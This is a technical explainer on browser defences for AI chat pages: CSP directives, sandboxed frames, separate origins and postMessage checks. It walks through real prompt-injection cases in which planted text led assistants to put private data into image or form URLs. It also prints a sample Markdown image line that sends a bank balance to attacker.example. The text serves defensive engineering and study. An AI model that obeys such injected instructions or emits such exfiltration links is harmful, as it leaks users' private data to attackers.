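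Lee and colleagues tried two remedies. One tied each tool's name to the origin that registered it and refused the same name from a different origin. The other limited what data the assistant could pass to tools from third-party origins. Each stopped all data theft in the attacks it targeted, even though the models still called the hostile tools in most attempts. Such rules can help when the hostile script comes from an advertising company's origin and the browser keeps track of that origin. But an event handler that the page inserts with a chat reply has no origin of its own, so an origin check would accept its tools as the bank's.

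## Limiting where a page can send data

Sending private data from a page to an attacker is called exfiltration. Besides `script-src`, a Content Security Policy has directives that limit which addresses the browser may contact. These can prevent exfiltration even after the earlier defences have failed.

### How an image address carries text

Suppose a customer asks the bank's assistant to review this month's payments, and one payment reference contains an attacker's instructions. They tell the model to end its reply with an image and to put the account balance in the image's address. The model writes this Markdown:

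```
![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=balance%204210%20EUR)
```

The part after the question mark is the query string, which normally passes details such as a search term to the server. An address cannot contain spaces, so each one becomes `%20`. The page converts the Markdown into an image tag, and the browser immediately requests the image. The attacker's server receives the whole address, including "balance 4210 EUR", and can save it in a log without sending back an image.

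The customer clicks nothing, and no script runs. A sanitiser that allows images leaves the tag in place, as happened with GitLab Duo.

### The directives for outgoing traffic

The relevant directive depends on how the data would leave:

| Directive | What it limits | How data could leave |
|---|---|---|
| `img-src` | Images | In the image's address |
| `connect-src` | Connections opened by scripts, including `fetch` and WebSockets | In the address or the body of a request |
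| `frame-src` | Pages shown in frames | In the frame's address |
| `form-action` | Where the page can submit forms | In the form's fields |

Fonts, style sheets and media have their own directives, which fall back to `default-src` as `script-src` does. `form-action` does not fall back to it, so a site has to set `form-action` explicitly.

W3C warns that a policy without `default-src` cannot prevent exfiltration, because some requests have no directive of their own, such as prefetches, which load resources the user may need next. A single loose directive also allows exfiltration, even if the others are strict. With `default-src 'none'; img-src *`, a page can send data to any server by putting it in an image URL.

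The bank could combine these limits with its nonce policy:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none';
  script-src 'nonce-q7Vd…' 'strict-dynamic'; style-src 'self';
  img-src 'self'; connect-src 'self'; form-action 'self'; base-uri 'none'
```

The browser would then block the request for the attacker's logo, so the balance would stay in the page. It would also block a `fetch` request to an outside server, which an injected script might use to send a whole conversation.

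### Why lists of permitted addresses failed

Most reported leaks from AI assistants did not require script, because the attacker got the model to write a link or an image. Willison had tagged 41 blog posts about exfiltration from chatbots by December 2025, and describes Markdown images as a common method.

Several of the affected products already had a policy that restricted images, but each policy permitted a host that the attacker could use:

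| Product | Permitted entry | How the data reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2025 | `*.teams.microsoft.com` | A Teams server requested the attacker's address |
| Salesforce Agentforce, 2025 | `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` | The domain had expired, and researchers registered it |
| Superhuman, 2025–26 | `docs.google.com` | Google Forms saved the data as a form response |
| Writer, 2023 | `*.cloudfront.net` | The attacker had a server address on CloudFront |
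| Google Bard, 2023 | `*.google.com` | The attacker ran code on a Google service |

#### A host that passes requests on

The attack on Copilot is called EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) explains how researchers at Aim Labs could steal data by sending an employee one email.

The email never mentioned AI and addressed its instructions to the human recipient, so Microsoft's filter for injected prompts did not flag it. The email repeated the instructions under headings such as "HR FAQs" and "leave of absence management", which made Copilot more likely to retrieve it when the employee asked about everyday topics. The model then put the most sensitive information it had into an image address.

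Microsoft's filter removed outside links and images from replies only if they were written in the usual Markdown form. It missed another Markdown form, which puts the address on a separate line and refers to it by a label.

The Content Security Policy (CSP) still blocked the attacker's server, but its `img-src` list had 29 different entries, 11 of which covered every subdomain of a domain. The researchers searched these hosts for a service that would forward a request to the attacker's server. They found one in SharePoint, but it required the employee to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service worked without any action from the employee. The browser requested an address on the Teams server, which then requested the attacker's address with the secret in it. CSP didn't block this second request because it only restricts requests made by the browser.

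Willison calls the Teams address an open redirect, which sends the browser to any address the visitor supplies, but Ravia describes a server that fetches the supplied address itself. The browser would have blocked a redirect from Teams to the attacker, because W3C's rules require it to check every address in a chain of redirects. Report URI's *Connection Allowlist* is therefore wrong to suggest that `connect-src` lets a permitted host redirect a request anywhere.

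Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers in May 2025, before the researchers published it in June. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had not affected any customers.

#### A domain that expired

In the ForcedLeak attack on Salesforce, researchers at Noma Security put instructions in a public web form of the kind Salesforce customers use to collect sales enquiries. When an employee asked the Agentforce assistant about the enquiry, the model collected sales contacts' email addresses and added them to the URL of an image.

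The policy permitted images from a domain that Salesforce no longer owned. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could have bought the domain for $5. The researchers registered it and received the contact data on their own server.

According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, Salesforce received a report of the vulnerability on July 28, 2025. The company took back the domain and corrected its policy. On September 8, it began checking the addresses its assistants produce.

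#### Hosts that store what they receive

The policy in the email application Superhuman permitted a host that was working normally. *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, by the security firm PromptArmor, describes an attack that began with a message the user had not opened. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant read hidden instructions in that message to include a feedback form.

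The form was a Google Form belonging to the attacker. Google lets people put answers in a form's address, so that opening the address submits them. The assistant put the user's emails in the form's address and used that address as the source of an image. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form. In tests, one reply leaked the full text of several emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

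PromptArmor reported this on Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features the following Monday and released further fixes until January 11, 2026. The same trick later worked on OpenAI's Codex, according to PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data*. PromptArmor reported that flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI has fixed it.

Willison described two earlier cases in 2023. Google's Bard chatbot could load images from any Google subdomain, including one where anyone can run their own code through Apps Script. Writer, an AI writing service, allowed images from any address on CloudFront, a content delivery network with many unrelated customers. Writer initially said the resulting data leak was not a security issue, but appeared to have fixed it by December 18, 2023.

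A list inside the application can fail in the same way. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes OpenAI's check for safe addresses, which accepted `windows.net`. Anyone can open a Microsoft storage account on that domain and read the log of requests to it.

Before permitting a host, site operators need to check whether outsiders can publish there, read its logs or make it fetch other addresses. They also need to check regularly that each permitted domain still belongs to the expected owner.

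### Checking addresses before displaying them

Salesforce's second fix, Trusted URLs, applies to the assistant's output as well as the browser. In The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025), the company says its services will enforce a list of trusted addresses so that prompt injection cannot make the assistant call or write a malicious link. According to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, administrators had to add every outside domain their assistants needed or risk disruption.

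This covers links, which CSP does not check when a user clicks them, but the list can include an unsuitable host. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of an address to trust, so that the assistant can use Google Drive files. Superhuman leaked emails through that host. A check of the host alone cannot distinguish a document from an attacker's form, though the example does not prove that Agentforce would load a form as an image.

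A site can also check where an address came from. Glean's *Untrusted URL monitoring*, the documentation for a feature of a workplace AI assistant, describes a filter that keeps an address if the user supplied it, a trusted tool returned it, or it is on a trusted domain. The filter can remove any other address, including one the model made up. This should catch an image address that the model has added a bank balance to, unless the domain is trusted. An attacker might get around the filter by supplying a complete address for each possible answer and asking the model to choose one. The filter would keep the chosen address if the site trusted the tool that returned the attacker's text.

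Neither check stops an injected script, which can send data without putting an address in a reply.

### Which measures could have stopped EchoLeak

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) compares eight measures against the steps of the attack. In the table, "yes" means Reddy and Gujral expect the measure to stop that step, "no" means they expect it to fail, and a dash means it does not apply.

| Measure | Outside email steers the model to private data | Email passes the prompt filter | Link passes the link filter | Browser fetches the image | Permitted host passes on the request | Data leaves without a click |
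|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Labelling outside text in the prompt | Yes | Yes | – | – | – | No |
| Using only internal sources by default | Yes | – | Yes | – | – | No |
| Restricting the format of replies | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | – | No |
| Permitting or blocking listed addresses | – | – | Yes | No | Yes | Yes |
| Strict CSP for images and connections | – | – | – | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Image proxy that requires signed addresses | – | – | – | Yes | Yes | Yes |
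| Human approval for outside content | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | – | Yes |
| Monitoring outgoing data | – | – | – | – | – | No |

The table is theoretical. Reddy and Gujral mention "our tests" in one sentence, but state elsewhere that they did not reproduce the attack or run any experiments.

Some of the table's entries are also questionable. According to the paper, EchoLeak "fails by design" if an assistant never uses outside emails to answer questions about internal projects, yet the table lists using only internal sources as a defense that would not stop the leak. The entry for a strict CSP is correct only if the policy allows no host that forwards requests, since Microsoft already had a CSP and it did not stop the leak.

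An image proxy is a server that fetches images for the page, so the browser never contacts other hosts. It must accept only addresses that the site has approved and signed. If it fetches every address it receives, it creates the same problem as the Teams service. The site must also not automatically sign every image address the model writes.

### Channels that CSP leaves open

A script can navigate the page to the attacker's address, with part of the conversation in the query string. `form-action` restricts form submissions, but the current CSP draft has no directive for ordinary navigation. The customer might notice the page changing, though the attacker's server could quickly redirect the browser back.

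Links can leak data in the same way when the user clicks them. EchoLeak first used a link before the researchers switched to an image. Links can also lead to phishing pages. In May 2026, The Hacker News reported that ChatGPT displayed live links and images from web pages it had summarised. An attacker could use them to show a false security alert, or a QR code that the user would scan with a phone, bypassing filters on the computer.

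WebRTC, the browser feature behind many video calls, lets a script open a data connection that `connect-src` does not cover. According to CentralCSP, criminals used it in 2026 to steal card details from a page that restricted `connect-src`. The CSP draft includes a directive, `webrtc 'block'`, that would block these connections, but browsers have not implemented it.

A comment on *Implement CSP 'webrtc' directive*, Mozilla's tracking page for adding the directive to Firefox, says that preventing exfiltration was never a stated goal of CSP. W3C's draft does say that lists of permitted servers can reduce exfiltration, though it does not guarantee complete protection.

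Data can also leave through the domain name system (DNS), which the browser uses to find a host's numerical address before connecting to it. A script could put data in a hostname, such as `balance-4210-eur.attacker.example`, and request a lookup. The lookup can reach the attacker's name server, which records the name, even if the browser never connects to the host.

The site's own functions are harder to restrict because the page needs them. If the bank lets customers email a statement to an accountant, an injected script could enter the attacker's address instead. The request goes to the bank's own server, so `connect-src 'self'` permits it.

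The assistant's tools can also send data without involving the browser. Superhuman's assistant could open web pages to answer questions, and PromptArmor found that a hidden instruction could make it open an attacker's address with private email text attached. In PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration in OpenAI Agent Builder via MCP*, an attacker filled in a sales form and got an assistant to email them customer data. The site's server has to control these tools. According to its *Security Advisories*, Salesforce began requiring confirmation in August 2025 before an assistant could use some Salesforce tools for actions such as cancelling an order or resetting a password.

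### Connection Allowlists

A newer browser feature, Connection Allowlists, applies one list to nearly all of a page's network connections. In the draft specification, *Connection Allowlists*, West argues that separate lists for images, fonts and scripts make little sense for preventing leaks, because data leaked through a font request is just as exposed as data leaked through an image request.

A site sends its list in a separate header:

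```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://cdn.example.net/images/*")
```

The word `response-origin` stands for the page's own origin. Helme explains in *Connection Allowlist* that the browser checks ordinary requests, page navigation and DNS prefetching against the list. It blocks WebRTC and redirects unless the site allows them with `webrtc=allow` or `redirects=allow`. Blocking redirects also makes it safer to allow only certain paths on a host, because an attacker cannot use a redirect to bypass the path restriction, as they can with CSP.

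Chrome tested the feature in versions 148 to 151 and released it in version 152, which Chrome for Developers (2026) announced on August 25. In September, Report URI said only Chromium-based browsers supported it. CentralCSP's *Connection Allowlists, a network egress sandbox in the browser* says Firefox and Safari had not signalled support. A site still needs a strict CSP for visitors using those browsers.

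The new header can also break services the site needs. Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026) warns that a list may block sign-in through an outside identity provider unless the site adds the provider's addresses. As with CSP, developers can first use a report-only version of the header to look for such problems.

Connection Allowlists limit where an injected script can send data but do not stop it from running. They do not help if the list permits a host that stores data for the attacker, and `response-origin` leaves the site's own functions available to the script. They also do not restrict the assistant's tools on the server.

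The list applies to one document, not to the whole origin. West warns that an injected script may be able to reach another page on the same origin with a looser list. On the bank's site, the script could open a help page with a looser list in a new window and send the conversation from there. A service worker can also have a different list from the page whose requests it handles.

West recommends avoiding this by sandboxing the restricted document so it no longer shares an origin with other pages. The document could still pass data to another page through `postMessage`, the browser function for sending messages between windows and frames, because the list covers only network connections. Chromium's developers also plan to let a host page set the list for a frame it embeds, according to their *Intent to Prototype*. A site could then restrict where a chat vendor's frame sends data, instead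 of relying on the vendor to do so.

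## Sandboxed frames and separate origins

The defences described so far leave the assistant in the same page as any script an attacker injects. A frame can separate them if its origin differs from the host page's.

Some sites use a frame to isolate content that the assistant wrote, which protects the chat page from that content. Others put the assistant itself in a frame to protect it from the host page.

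### What the sandbox attribute withholds

A site sandboxes a frame by adding the `sandbox` attribute to its tag:

```html
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts" src="https://preview.example.net/chart"></iframe>
```

If the sandbox attribute is empty, the browser stops the framed content from running scripts, submitting forms, opening new windows or navigating the rest of the tab. It also gives the content an opaque origin, which matches no other origin, so the content cannot read the bank's cookies, browser storage or the surrounding page, even if the bank's own server sent the file.

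The site can restore individual powers with keywords. WHATWG's *The iframe element* defines more than a dozen, including these:

| Keyword | What it restores |
|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | Running JavaScript |
| `allow-same-origin` | The content's real origin, with its cookies and storage |
| `allow-forms` | Submitting forms |
| `allow-popups` | Opening new windows, which stay sandboxed unless another keyword frees them |
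| `allow-top-navigation` | Sending the whole tab to another address |
| `allow-downloads` | Downloading files |

A frame inside another frame is subject to the restrictions of both, so if the outer frame blocks scripts, the inner one cannot turn them back on. The browser applies the keywords when it loads a document into the frame, so a site that tightens the attribute later does not affect the document already loaded.

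The `sandbox` attribute does not limit network connections, so a frame with `allow-scripts` can send anything it can read to any server unless a CSP prevents it.

### Two permissions that cancel the sandbox

Suppose the bank's assistant writes an interactive spending chart, and the bank displays it in a frame served from the bank's own origin. The chart needs to run scripts, so the bank grants `allow-scripts`. It also needs to remember the customer's settings, so the bank adds `allow-same-origin`.

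The chart's code now has the bank's origin, so it can read the host page directly. It can also remove the `sandbox` attribute from its own frame and reload the frame without the sandbox's restrictions.

Combining `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin` does not expose the host page if the framed content comes from a different origin, because `allow-same-origin` restores only that other origin. The documentation for A2UI, a system for displaying interfaces that AI agents supply, overstates the problem by warning that any frame with both keywords can escape. Still, A2UI's rule of never granting `allow-same-origin` to the frame with the untrusted code is easier to check than where each file came from.

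### A separate domain and a separate process

A sandboxed frame does not help if the victim opens the untrusted file outside it. An attacker could send a customer a direct link to the chart, and if the customer opened it, the chart's script would run with the bank's origin. WHATWG therefore recommends serving such files from a dedicated domain. The server can also send the restrictions in CSP's `sandbox` directive, which the browser applies even on a direct visit.

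A different port or subdomain also creates a separate origin, but it separates less than a new domain does. For a host page at `https://www.example.com`:

| Address of the frame | Separate origin? | Can it receive the host's cookies? | Separate process in desktop Chrome? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://www.example.com:8443` | Yes | Yes, because cookies ignore the port | Not by default |
| `https://chat.example.com` | Yes | Yes, if the site sets them for the whole domain | Not by default |
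| `https://assistant.example.net` | Yes | No | Yes |

OpenClaw, an AI assistant that people run themselves, uses a second port for interfaces from outside tools. Its documentation tells operators not to use that origin to host anything sensitive or anything that requires a sign-in.

The last column matters when the browser itself has a bug. A browser draws pages in renderer processes, and the operating system keeps one process from reading another's memory. According to Chromium's *Site Isolation Design Document*, before version 67 Chrome sometimes ran a frame from another site in the host page's process and relied on that process to enforce the same-origin policy. An attacker who used a bug to take over the process could bypass the policy.

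Chrome now puts documents from different sites in different renderer processes. Chromium's *Site Isolation* explains that Chrome also withholds data such as HTML and JSON from another site's process unless the server permits access. *Process Model and Site Isolation* describes how a more privileged browser process monitors each renderer's requests.

Site isolation is more limited on phones. Chrome on Android isolates only some sites, mainly ones where people sign in. As of 2024, Chromium listed site isolation as unavailable on Android phones with under 2 GB of memory, in Android WebView, which displays web pages inside apps, and in Chrome for iOS. The same-origin policy still applies without site isolation, but a single browser bug could defeat it.

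Chrome ignores subdomains when deciding what counts as a site, so two pieces of untrusted content on subdomains of one domain may share a process. assistant-ui's *Safe Content Frame*, a component for chat pages, avoids this by giving each piece a new hostname under a public suffix, which is an ending such as `co.uk` under which unrelated people can register names. Browsers treat each of those names as a separate site.

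### Pages that the assistant writes

Claude can write small web pages called artifacts, such as a dashboard or a calculator, and display them to the user. An artifact may contain any JavaScript the model produces, including code that an attacker got it to write. *How Anthropic built Artifacts* (Willison, 2024) quotes Anthropic employees who said they put artifacts in sandboxed frames with a separate process to protect the user's main Claude session, and used strict CSPs to limit network access.

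Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Artifacts* tested how well this works. Anthropic served each web artifact from its own subdomain of `claudeusercontent.com`, so artifacts could not read each other or the Claude page. The policy limited connections to the artifact's own origin but allowed inline scripts and `eval()`. Allowing these would be a serious weakness on the chat page, but it matters little in a frame meant to run arbitrary code.

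The firm built an artifact that tried to reach an outside server through `fetch`, an older request function, a WebSocket, an image and `sendBeacon()`. The browser blocked all five. The test did not cover DNS lookups, navigation or WebRTC. Anthropic's policy includes `webrtc 'block'`, which browsers do not yet enforce.

Anthropic's more recent documentation lists outside hosts that do not appear in the part of the policy Pluto Security published. Artifacts can load JavaScript libraries from five public hosts, including `unpkg.com` and `cdn.jsdelivr.net`, and fonts from Google. These hosts don't give the artifact any new power to run code, since it can already run whatever it contains. They could help an attacker exfiltrate data only if the attacker could find out what the artifact requested from them.

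ChatGPT also displays HTML previews in sandboxed frames. According to Willison's summary of the October 2026 attack, code in a preview escaped its frame by sending a message that the surrounding ChatGPT page handled unsafely.

### A policy placed inside the frame

Running a second domain is extra work for a small site. While building his own version of artifacts, Willison (2026), in *Can JavaScript Escape a CSP Meta Tag Inside an Iframe?*, looked for a way to restrict a frame's network access without one. A page can carry a CSP in a `meta` tag instead of an HTTP header, so he put one at the top of the frame's content, before the untrusted code:

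```html
<meta http-equiv="Content-Security-Policy"
      content="default-src 'none'; script-src 'unsafe-inline'">
```

Untrusted code can't remove the policy by deleting the tag, because the browser adopts the policy when it parses the tag. In Willison's tests on Chromium and Firefox, the policy stayed in force when the code removed the tag, changed it or replaced the whole document. It also stayed in force when the code navigated the frame to a `data:` address, which contains a page's contents in the address itself.

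Willison then used this technique in Datasette, a tool for exploring databases, to run untrusted apps on the same domain as private data. *Datasette Apps* combines a `meta` policy with `sandbox="allow-scripts"` and the `srcdoc` attribute, which lets the host page supply the frame's HTML directly.

Apps displayed this way have an opaque origin, so they cannot use cookies or browser storage. A `srcdoc` frame also inherits the host page's CSP, so if that policy requires a nonce for every script, the browser will block the app's scripts even though the `meta` tag allows inline code. A site would have to choose between a strict policy on its chat page and this method of displaying apps.

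The `meta` policy also does not stop the code from navigating its frame to an attacker's address with data in the query string. The host page has to limit that with its own `frame-src` directive.

In another of Willison's experiments, the user could weaken the confinement. The frame reported each connection that the policy blocked, and the host page then offered to add the address to the permitted list. This is convenient for someone building an app, but a hostile app can try to connect to its author's server, and the address will be permitted if the user presses "OK".

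### Calls from an artifact back to the assistant

Strict confinement also blocks useful features. In 2024, Willison noted that people couldn't build an artifact that analysed images with Claude, because the CSP stopped the artifact's code from contacting a model.

Anthropic removed that limit in June 2025 with a function called `window.claude.complete()`, which Willison said "opens a hole" in the sandbox. The artifact passes the function a prompt and receives Claude's answer as text. Each visitor signs in to their own Claude account, and the prompt counts toward that account's usage.

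The function originally did not give the model earlier conversations, so an artifact had to include any history in its prompt. A hostile artifact could therefore use up a visitor's allowance, but it could not retrieve the visitor's past conversations just by prompting Claude. Anthropic changed the mechanism the following month.

Connectors weaken the frame's isolation more. They link Claude to the user's other services, such as a calendar, and an artifact can call them to show live data. The Claude page sends the request using the viewer's account, so the frame never holds a login token. Anthropic's documentation says that Claude's website asks each viewer for permission before the first call, and that the artifact can use only the connectors declared when it was published.

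Pluto Security confirmed that a colleague who opened its test artifact could not reach the author's calendar. But the viewer's own data may still be exposed, because an artifact can use connectors that post messages or change records. A viewer who approves them may give a hostile page a way to send data out. The frame's CSP would not block this because the surrounding page makes the request. Anthropic reduces the risk by refusing connector calls for viewers outside the publisher's organisation.

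### Interfaces from outside tools

Model Context Protocol (2026), the project behind a standard for connecting assistants to outside tools, launched an extension called MCP Apps in January 2026. It lets a tool return an interactive page, such as a form or a map, which the assistant displays in the conversation. Claude, ChatGPT and Visual Studio Code were among the first products to support it.

In these products, each app runs in a frame inside another frame. Barthelet (2026), in *Why MCP and ChatGPT Apps Use Double Iframes*, explains the reason by working through the simpler designs:

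| How the chat page loads the app | What goes wrong |
|---|---|
| Through `srcdoc`, with no sandbox | The app inherits the chat page's nonce policy, so its scripts fail. If the site loosened the policy, the app could read the site's storage. |
| Through `srcdoc`, with an opaque origin | The app loses cookies and storage. |
| Through `srcdoc`, with `allow-same-origin` | The app gets the chat page's origin and can leave the sandbox. |
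| From the developer's own server | The chat page has to permit every developer's domain in `frame-src`. |

The nested design uses a second domain that the chat company controls. Salomon, Yosef and colleagues (2025), in *SEP-1865*, set it out in the specification for MCP Apps:

1. The chat page opens an outer frame from a different origin, with `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin`.
2. A small loader in the outer frame tells the chat page that it is ready.
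3. The chat page sends the loader the app's HTML.
4. The loader puts the HTML in an inner frame, under a CSP based on the domains that the app's developer declared.
5. The loader passes messages between the app and the chat page, which decides whether to act on them.

The chat company can use the same loader file for every app, as long as it serves the file from a different subdomain for each one. Otherwise the apps would share browser storage. According to Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS*, Claude can give an app a stable subdomain of `claudemcpcontent.com`, named with a hash of the tool server's address. All apps from one server would get the same subdomain, so this method doesn't protect them from each other.

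Barthelet describes putting the CSP in the outer frame, so that it covers both the outer and inner frames. If the policy covered only the inner frame and that frame had `allow-same-origin`, the app could easily avoid it. The app would share an origin with the loader, so it could change the loader's document and open a new frame from the outer frame.

An app that declares no outside domains cannot connect to any. But the developer writes the declaration, so a dishonest developer can list a server that collects whatever the user types. The chat page may remove domains from the list or warn the user. The policy is better at stopping an outsider who injects script into an honest developer's app, since that script can contact only the declared domains.

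An app can also ask the chat page to call tools on the app's own server, open links, send messages to the conversation, and add text to what the model reads next. The specification allows the chat page to require the user's approval for tool calls but doesn't oblige it to. A hostile app can therefore attempt prompt injection through these requests even if it cannot read the chat page.

### What a frame can still show

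A frame limits what its code can reach but doesn't limit what that code can display. Eye Security built a fake login screen in a Gemini canvas, a shareable page made with Google's assistant, then pasted its HTML into ChatGPT's version of the feature. Gemini warned visitors that another person had created the page. The researchers expected the warning to make most people close the page but did not test this on real users.

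Salomon and colleagues list misleading content as a remaining risk of MCP Apps and advise chat pages to mark clearly where an app begins and ends. Anthropic's *Share artifacts* tells users to treat someone else's artifact like a file from an unknown sender.

An artifact can also contain secrets that its author did not mean to share. Pluto Security hid instructions in a fake guide that Claude's coding agent was following. In 10 of 85 attempts, the agent copied made-up login credentials from a local file into a hidden part of the artifact and published it. Anthropic's server did not inspect the content. The sandbox worked as intended, but anyone with access to the artifact could read the credentials in its source.

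### Keeping the assistant away from the host page

Suppose the bank puts the assistant itself in a frame from `assistant.example.net`, and an attacker injects script into the account page around it. The script can't read the conversation, type in the chat box or replace the frame's copy of `fetch`, so the most direct attacks described for code in the same context no longer work.

The injected script still controls everything around the frame, so it can:

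- remove the frame and draw a copy of the chat in its place. The customer has little chance of noticing, because the address bar shows the bank's real address with either version.
- cover part of the frame, such as the amount above an "Approve" button.
- give the assistant false context. Many sites pass the frame details such as the page the customer is viewing, and the script can change those details on the way.
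- make the frame transparent and place it over something harmless. The customer tries to close an advertisement but presses "Approve" in the hidden frame. This is called clickjacking, and the frame receives a real click that it can't distinguish from an intended one.

These attacks usually need the customer to type or click, and none of them exposes past conversations. That is an improvement over running the assistant in the host page.

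The setup code can undo much of this gain. With the hosted version of OpenAI's ChatKit, an injected script could request a client secret from the site's server, just as the host page does, and use it to start its own conversation.

### Which pages may embed the assistant

A hostile website can also embed a real assistant in its own page. The `frame-ancestors` directive prevents this by listing the pages that may put a document in a frame. The assistant's server sends it with the chat document:

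```
Content-Security-Policy: frame-ancestors https://www.example.com
```

The browser then refuses to display the chat unless every page that frames it, directly or indirectly, is on the list. The value `'none'` forbids all framing. The directive does not fall back to `default-src`, and it has no effect in a `meta` tag. When Pluto Security examined Claude's artifacts, the artifacts' policy allowed only Claude's own site and the artifact's origin to frame them. For artifacts published from a chat, users can list the websites that may embed them.

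Imperva's *XSS Marks the Spot* describes an attack that was possible because ChatGPT then let any site frame it. The server accepted messages that a user had labelled as the assistant's, with invented citations attached. The researcher used this to create and share a conversation with a citation whose link contained JavaScript.

Because the link opened in a new tab, the browser would run its code only if the victim held a modifier key while clicking. The researcher therefore built a website with the shared conversation in an invisible frame, positioned so that any click landed on the citation. The visible text asked visitors to hold the ⌘ key and click.

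The browser also withheld ChatGPT's session cookie and usual storage because ChatGPT was in a frame on another site, so the script ran in a signed-out page. The script then created a new document in ChatGPT's origin and navigated the whole tab to it. There the script was no longer in a frame, so it could use the victim's session and take over the account.

OpenAI fixed the flaw within hours by allowing only web, email and telephone addresses in citation links. The `frame-ancestors` directive would have blocked the invisible frame but would not have repaired the link, so someone who opened the shared conversation directly could still have clicked it.

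Imperva had found another flaw in how ChatGPT opened uploaded files that it cited. ChatGPT's CSP blocked the script in a test file at first. But the nonce was the same for every account and every visit, so the researcher copied it into the file.

`frame-ancestors` does not help when an attacker has injected script into the bank's page, because that page is on the list.

### When the separation holds

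A separate origin protects the conversation only if the host page cannot reach the conversation some other way. The host's origin must not also serve the chat history, for instance at an address that the old version of the chat used. The assistant's document must not load scripts from the host's server either, since an attacker who could change those files could then run code inside the frame.

The session has to be separate too. If the bank's main cookie also works at `chat.example.com`, a script in the account page can send requests there, and the browser will attach the cookie. The script cannot read the responses unless the chat server permits it, but the assistant may still carry out a prompt sent this way. Giving the assistant its own cookie is not enough, because the browser may attach that one as well. The chat server also has to refuse requests from the account page's origin.

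A separate session makes signing in harder. Browsers restrict cookies in frames from other sites, as Imperva's researcher found. Users of Microsoft's framed Copilot Studio agent have to copy a code from another tab. Passing a login token from the host page would be easier for users, but an injected script could steal it.

The last condition is a narrow message channel. A host page may need to send the frame a language setting or the window size, and a false value does little harm. A message that submits a prompt is far more dangerous. Corgea's *Open WebUI* describes a flaw (CVE-2026-54007) that let any website send such a message to Open WebUI's chat page, which then submitted the prompt in the signed-in user's session. The attack worked even though the sending site could not read the conversation.

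## Messages between frames and the ChatGPT bypass of October 2026

Other websites could submit prompts to Open WebUI's chat page through `postMessage`, the browser function that lets windows and frames from different origins exchange data. Most sites that put an assistant or its output in a frame need this function, but each message crosses the boundary that a separate origin creates, so the receiving page has to decide whether to act on it.

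### How a page sends and receives messages

Suppose the bank has put its assistant in a frame from `assistant.example.net`. A script in the account page can send it the customer's language like this:

```js
chatFrame.contentWindow.postMessage(
  { type: "set-language", language: "de" },
  "https://assistant.example.net"
);
```

The first argument is the data, which the browser copies to the receiving page. The second is the target origin, and the browser does not deliver the message if the frame has since moved to a page from another origin. A sender can turn this check off by writing `"*"`, which stands for any origin. Whatever page is in the frame then receives the data, which matters much more if the data is a login token than if it is a language setting.

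To receive messages, a page adds a listener, which is a function that the browser calls each time one arrives. The browser passes the listener an event object with these properties:

- `data` is what the sender wrote.
- `origin` is the sending page's origin.
- `source` is a reference to the sending window or frame.

The browser fills in the last two, so a hostile page can't fake them. But it delivers messages from any page that has a reference to the window. That could be a frame inside the page, a page that embeds it, or a website that opened it in a new tab. The listener has to reject unwanted messages. Libraries can add listeners too, and the browser calls every listener in the page for every message.

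### What a safe listener checks

The assistant's frame could receive the language setting with this listener:

```js
window.addEventListener("message", (event) => {
  if (event.origin !== "https://www.example.com") return;
  if (event.source !== window.parent) return;
  if (event.data?.type !== "set-language") return;
  if (!["en", "de", "fr"].includes(event.data.language)) return;
  setLanguage(event.data.language);
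});
```

The first check compares the whole origin. Developers sometimes only search the origin for their site's name, but a search for `example.com` also succeeds on `https://example.com.attacker.example`. The second check accepts messages only from the page that directly contains the frame, not from another of the bank's pages that has a reference to the frame.

The last two checks limit the message to one purpose and three values, so a false message that gets through can at worst put the chat in the wrong language. Open WebUI's listener let senders do much more, because it accepted `input:prompt` and `action:submit` messages until version 0.9.6, according to Vulners' *CVE-2026-54007*.

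A listener should also treat text in a message as plain text. If it passes the text to `innerHTML`, anyone who can send it a message can add markup to the page.

These checks don't protect the assistant's frame from a script that an attacker has injected into the account page, because the script's messages have the bank's origin and come from the expected window. The script can also add its own listener to the page and read whatever the frame sends back.

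### Frames whose origin is "null"

A sandboxed frame without `allow-same-origin` has an opaque origin, which the browser reports to message listeners as the string `"null"`. The browser reports the same value for every such frame, including one that an attacker creates on a hostile website, so a listener that accepts messages from `"null"` also accepts messages from the attacker's frame.

If the bank shows a spending chart in such a frame, the account page has to identify it by its window instead:

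```js
if (event.source !== chartFrame.contentWindow) return;
```

This check identifies the frame but not the page inside it. If the chart's code navigates the frame to an attacker's address, messages from the new page still pass. The account page should treat every message from the frame as untrusted, which it has to do anyway if a model wrote the chart's code.

The account page has a similar problem when it sends data to the chart, because an opaque origin has no address to specify as the target. The page has to use `"*"`, so it should send only data that another page could safely receive.

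### Private message channels

A page can avoid some of these difficulties by giving a frame its own channel. `MessageChannel` creates two connected ports, and whatever a script sends into one port comes out of the other. The page keeps one and sends the other to the frame:

```js
const channel = new MessageChannel();
channel.port1.onmessage = (event) => setChartHeight(event.data);
chartFrame.contentWindow.postMessage("connect", "*", [channel.port2]);
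```

After that, the account page no longer needs a general listener for the chart. Other frames and websites can't send messages through the channel because they don't have a port. The browser doesn't report an origin for these messages, so the channel's security depends on which page received the port. A channel is safer than checking `event.source` alone because, if the frame later loads another page, that page doesn't inherit the port.

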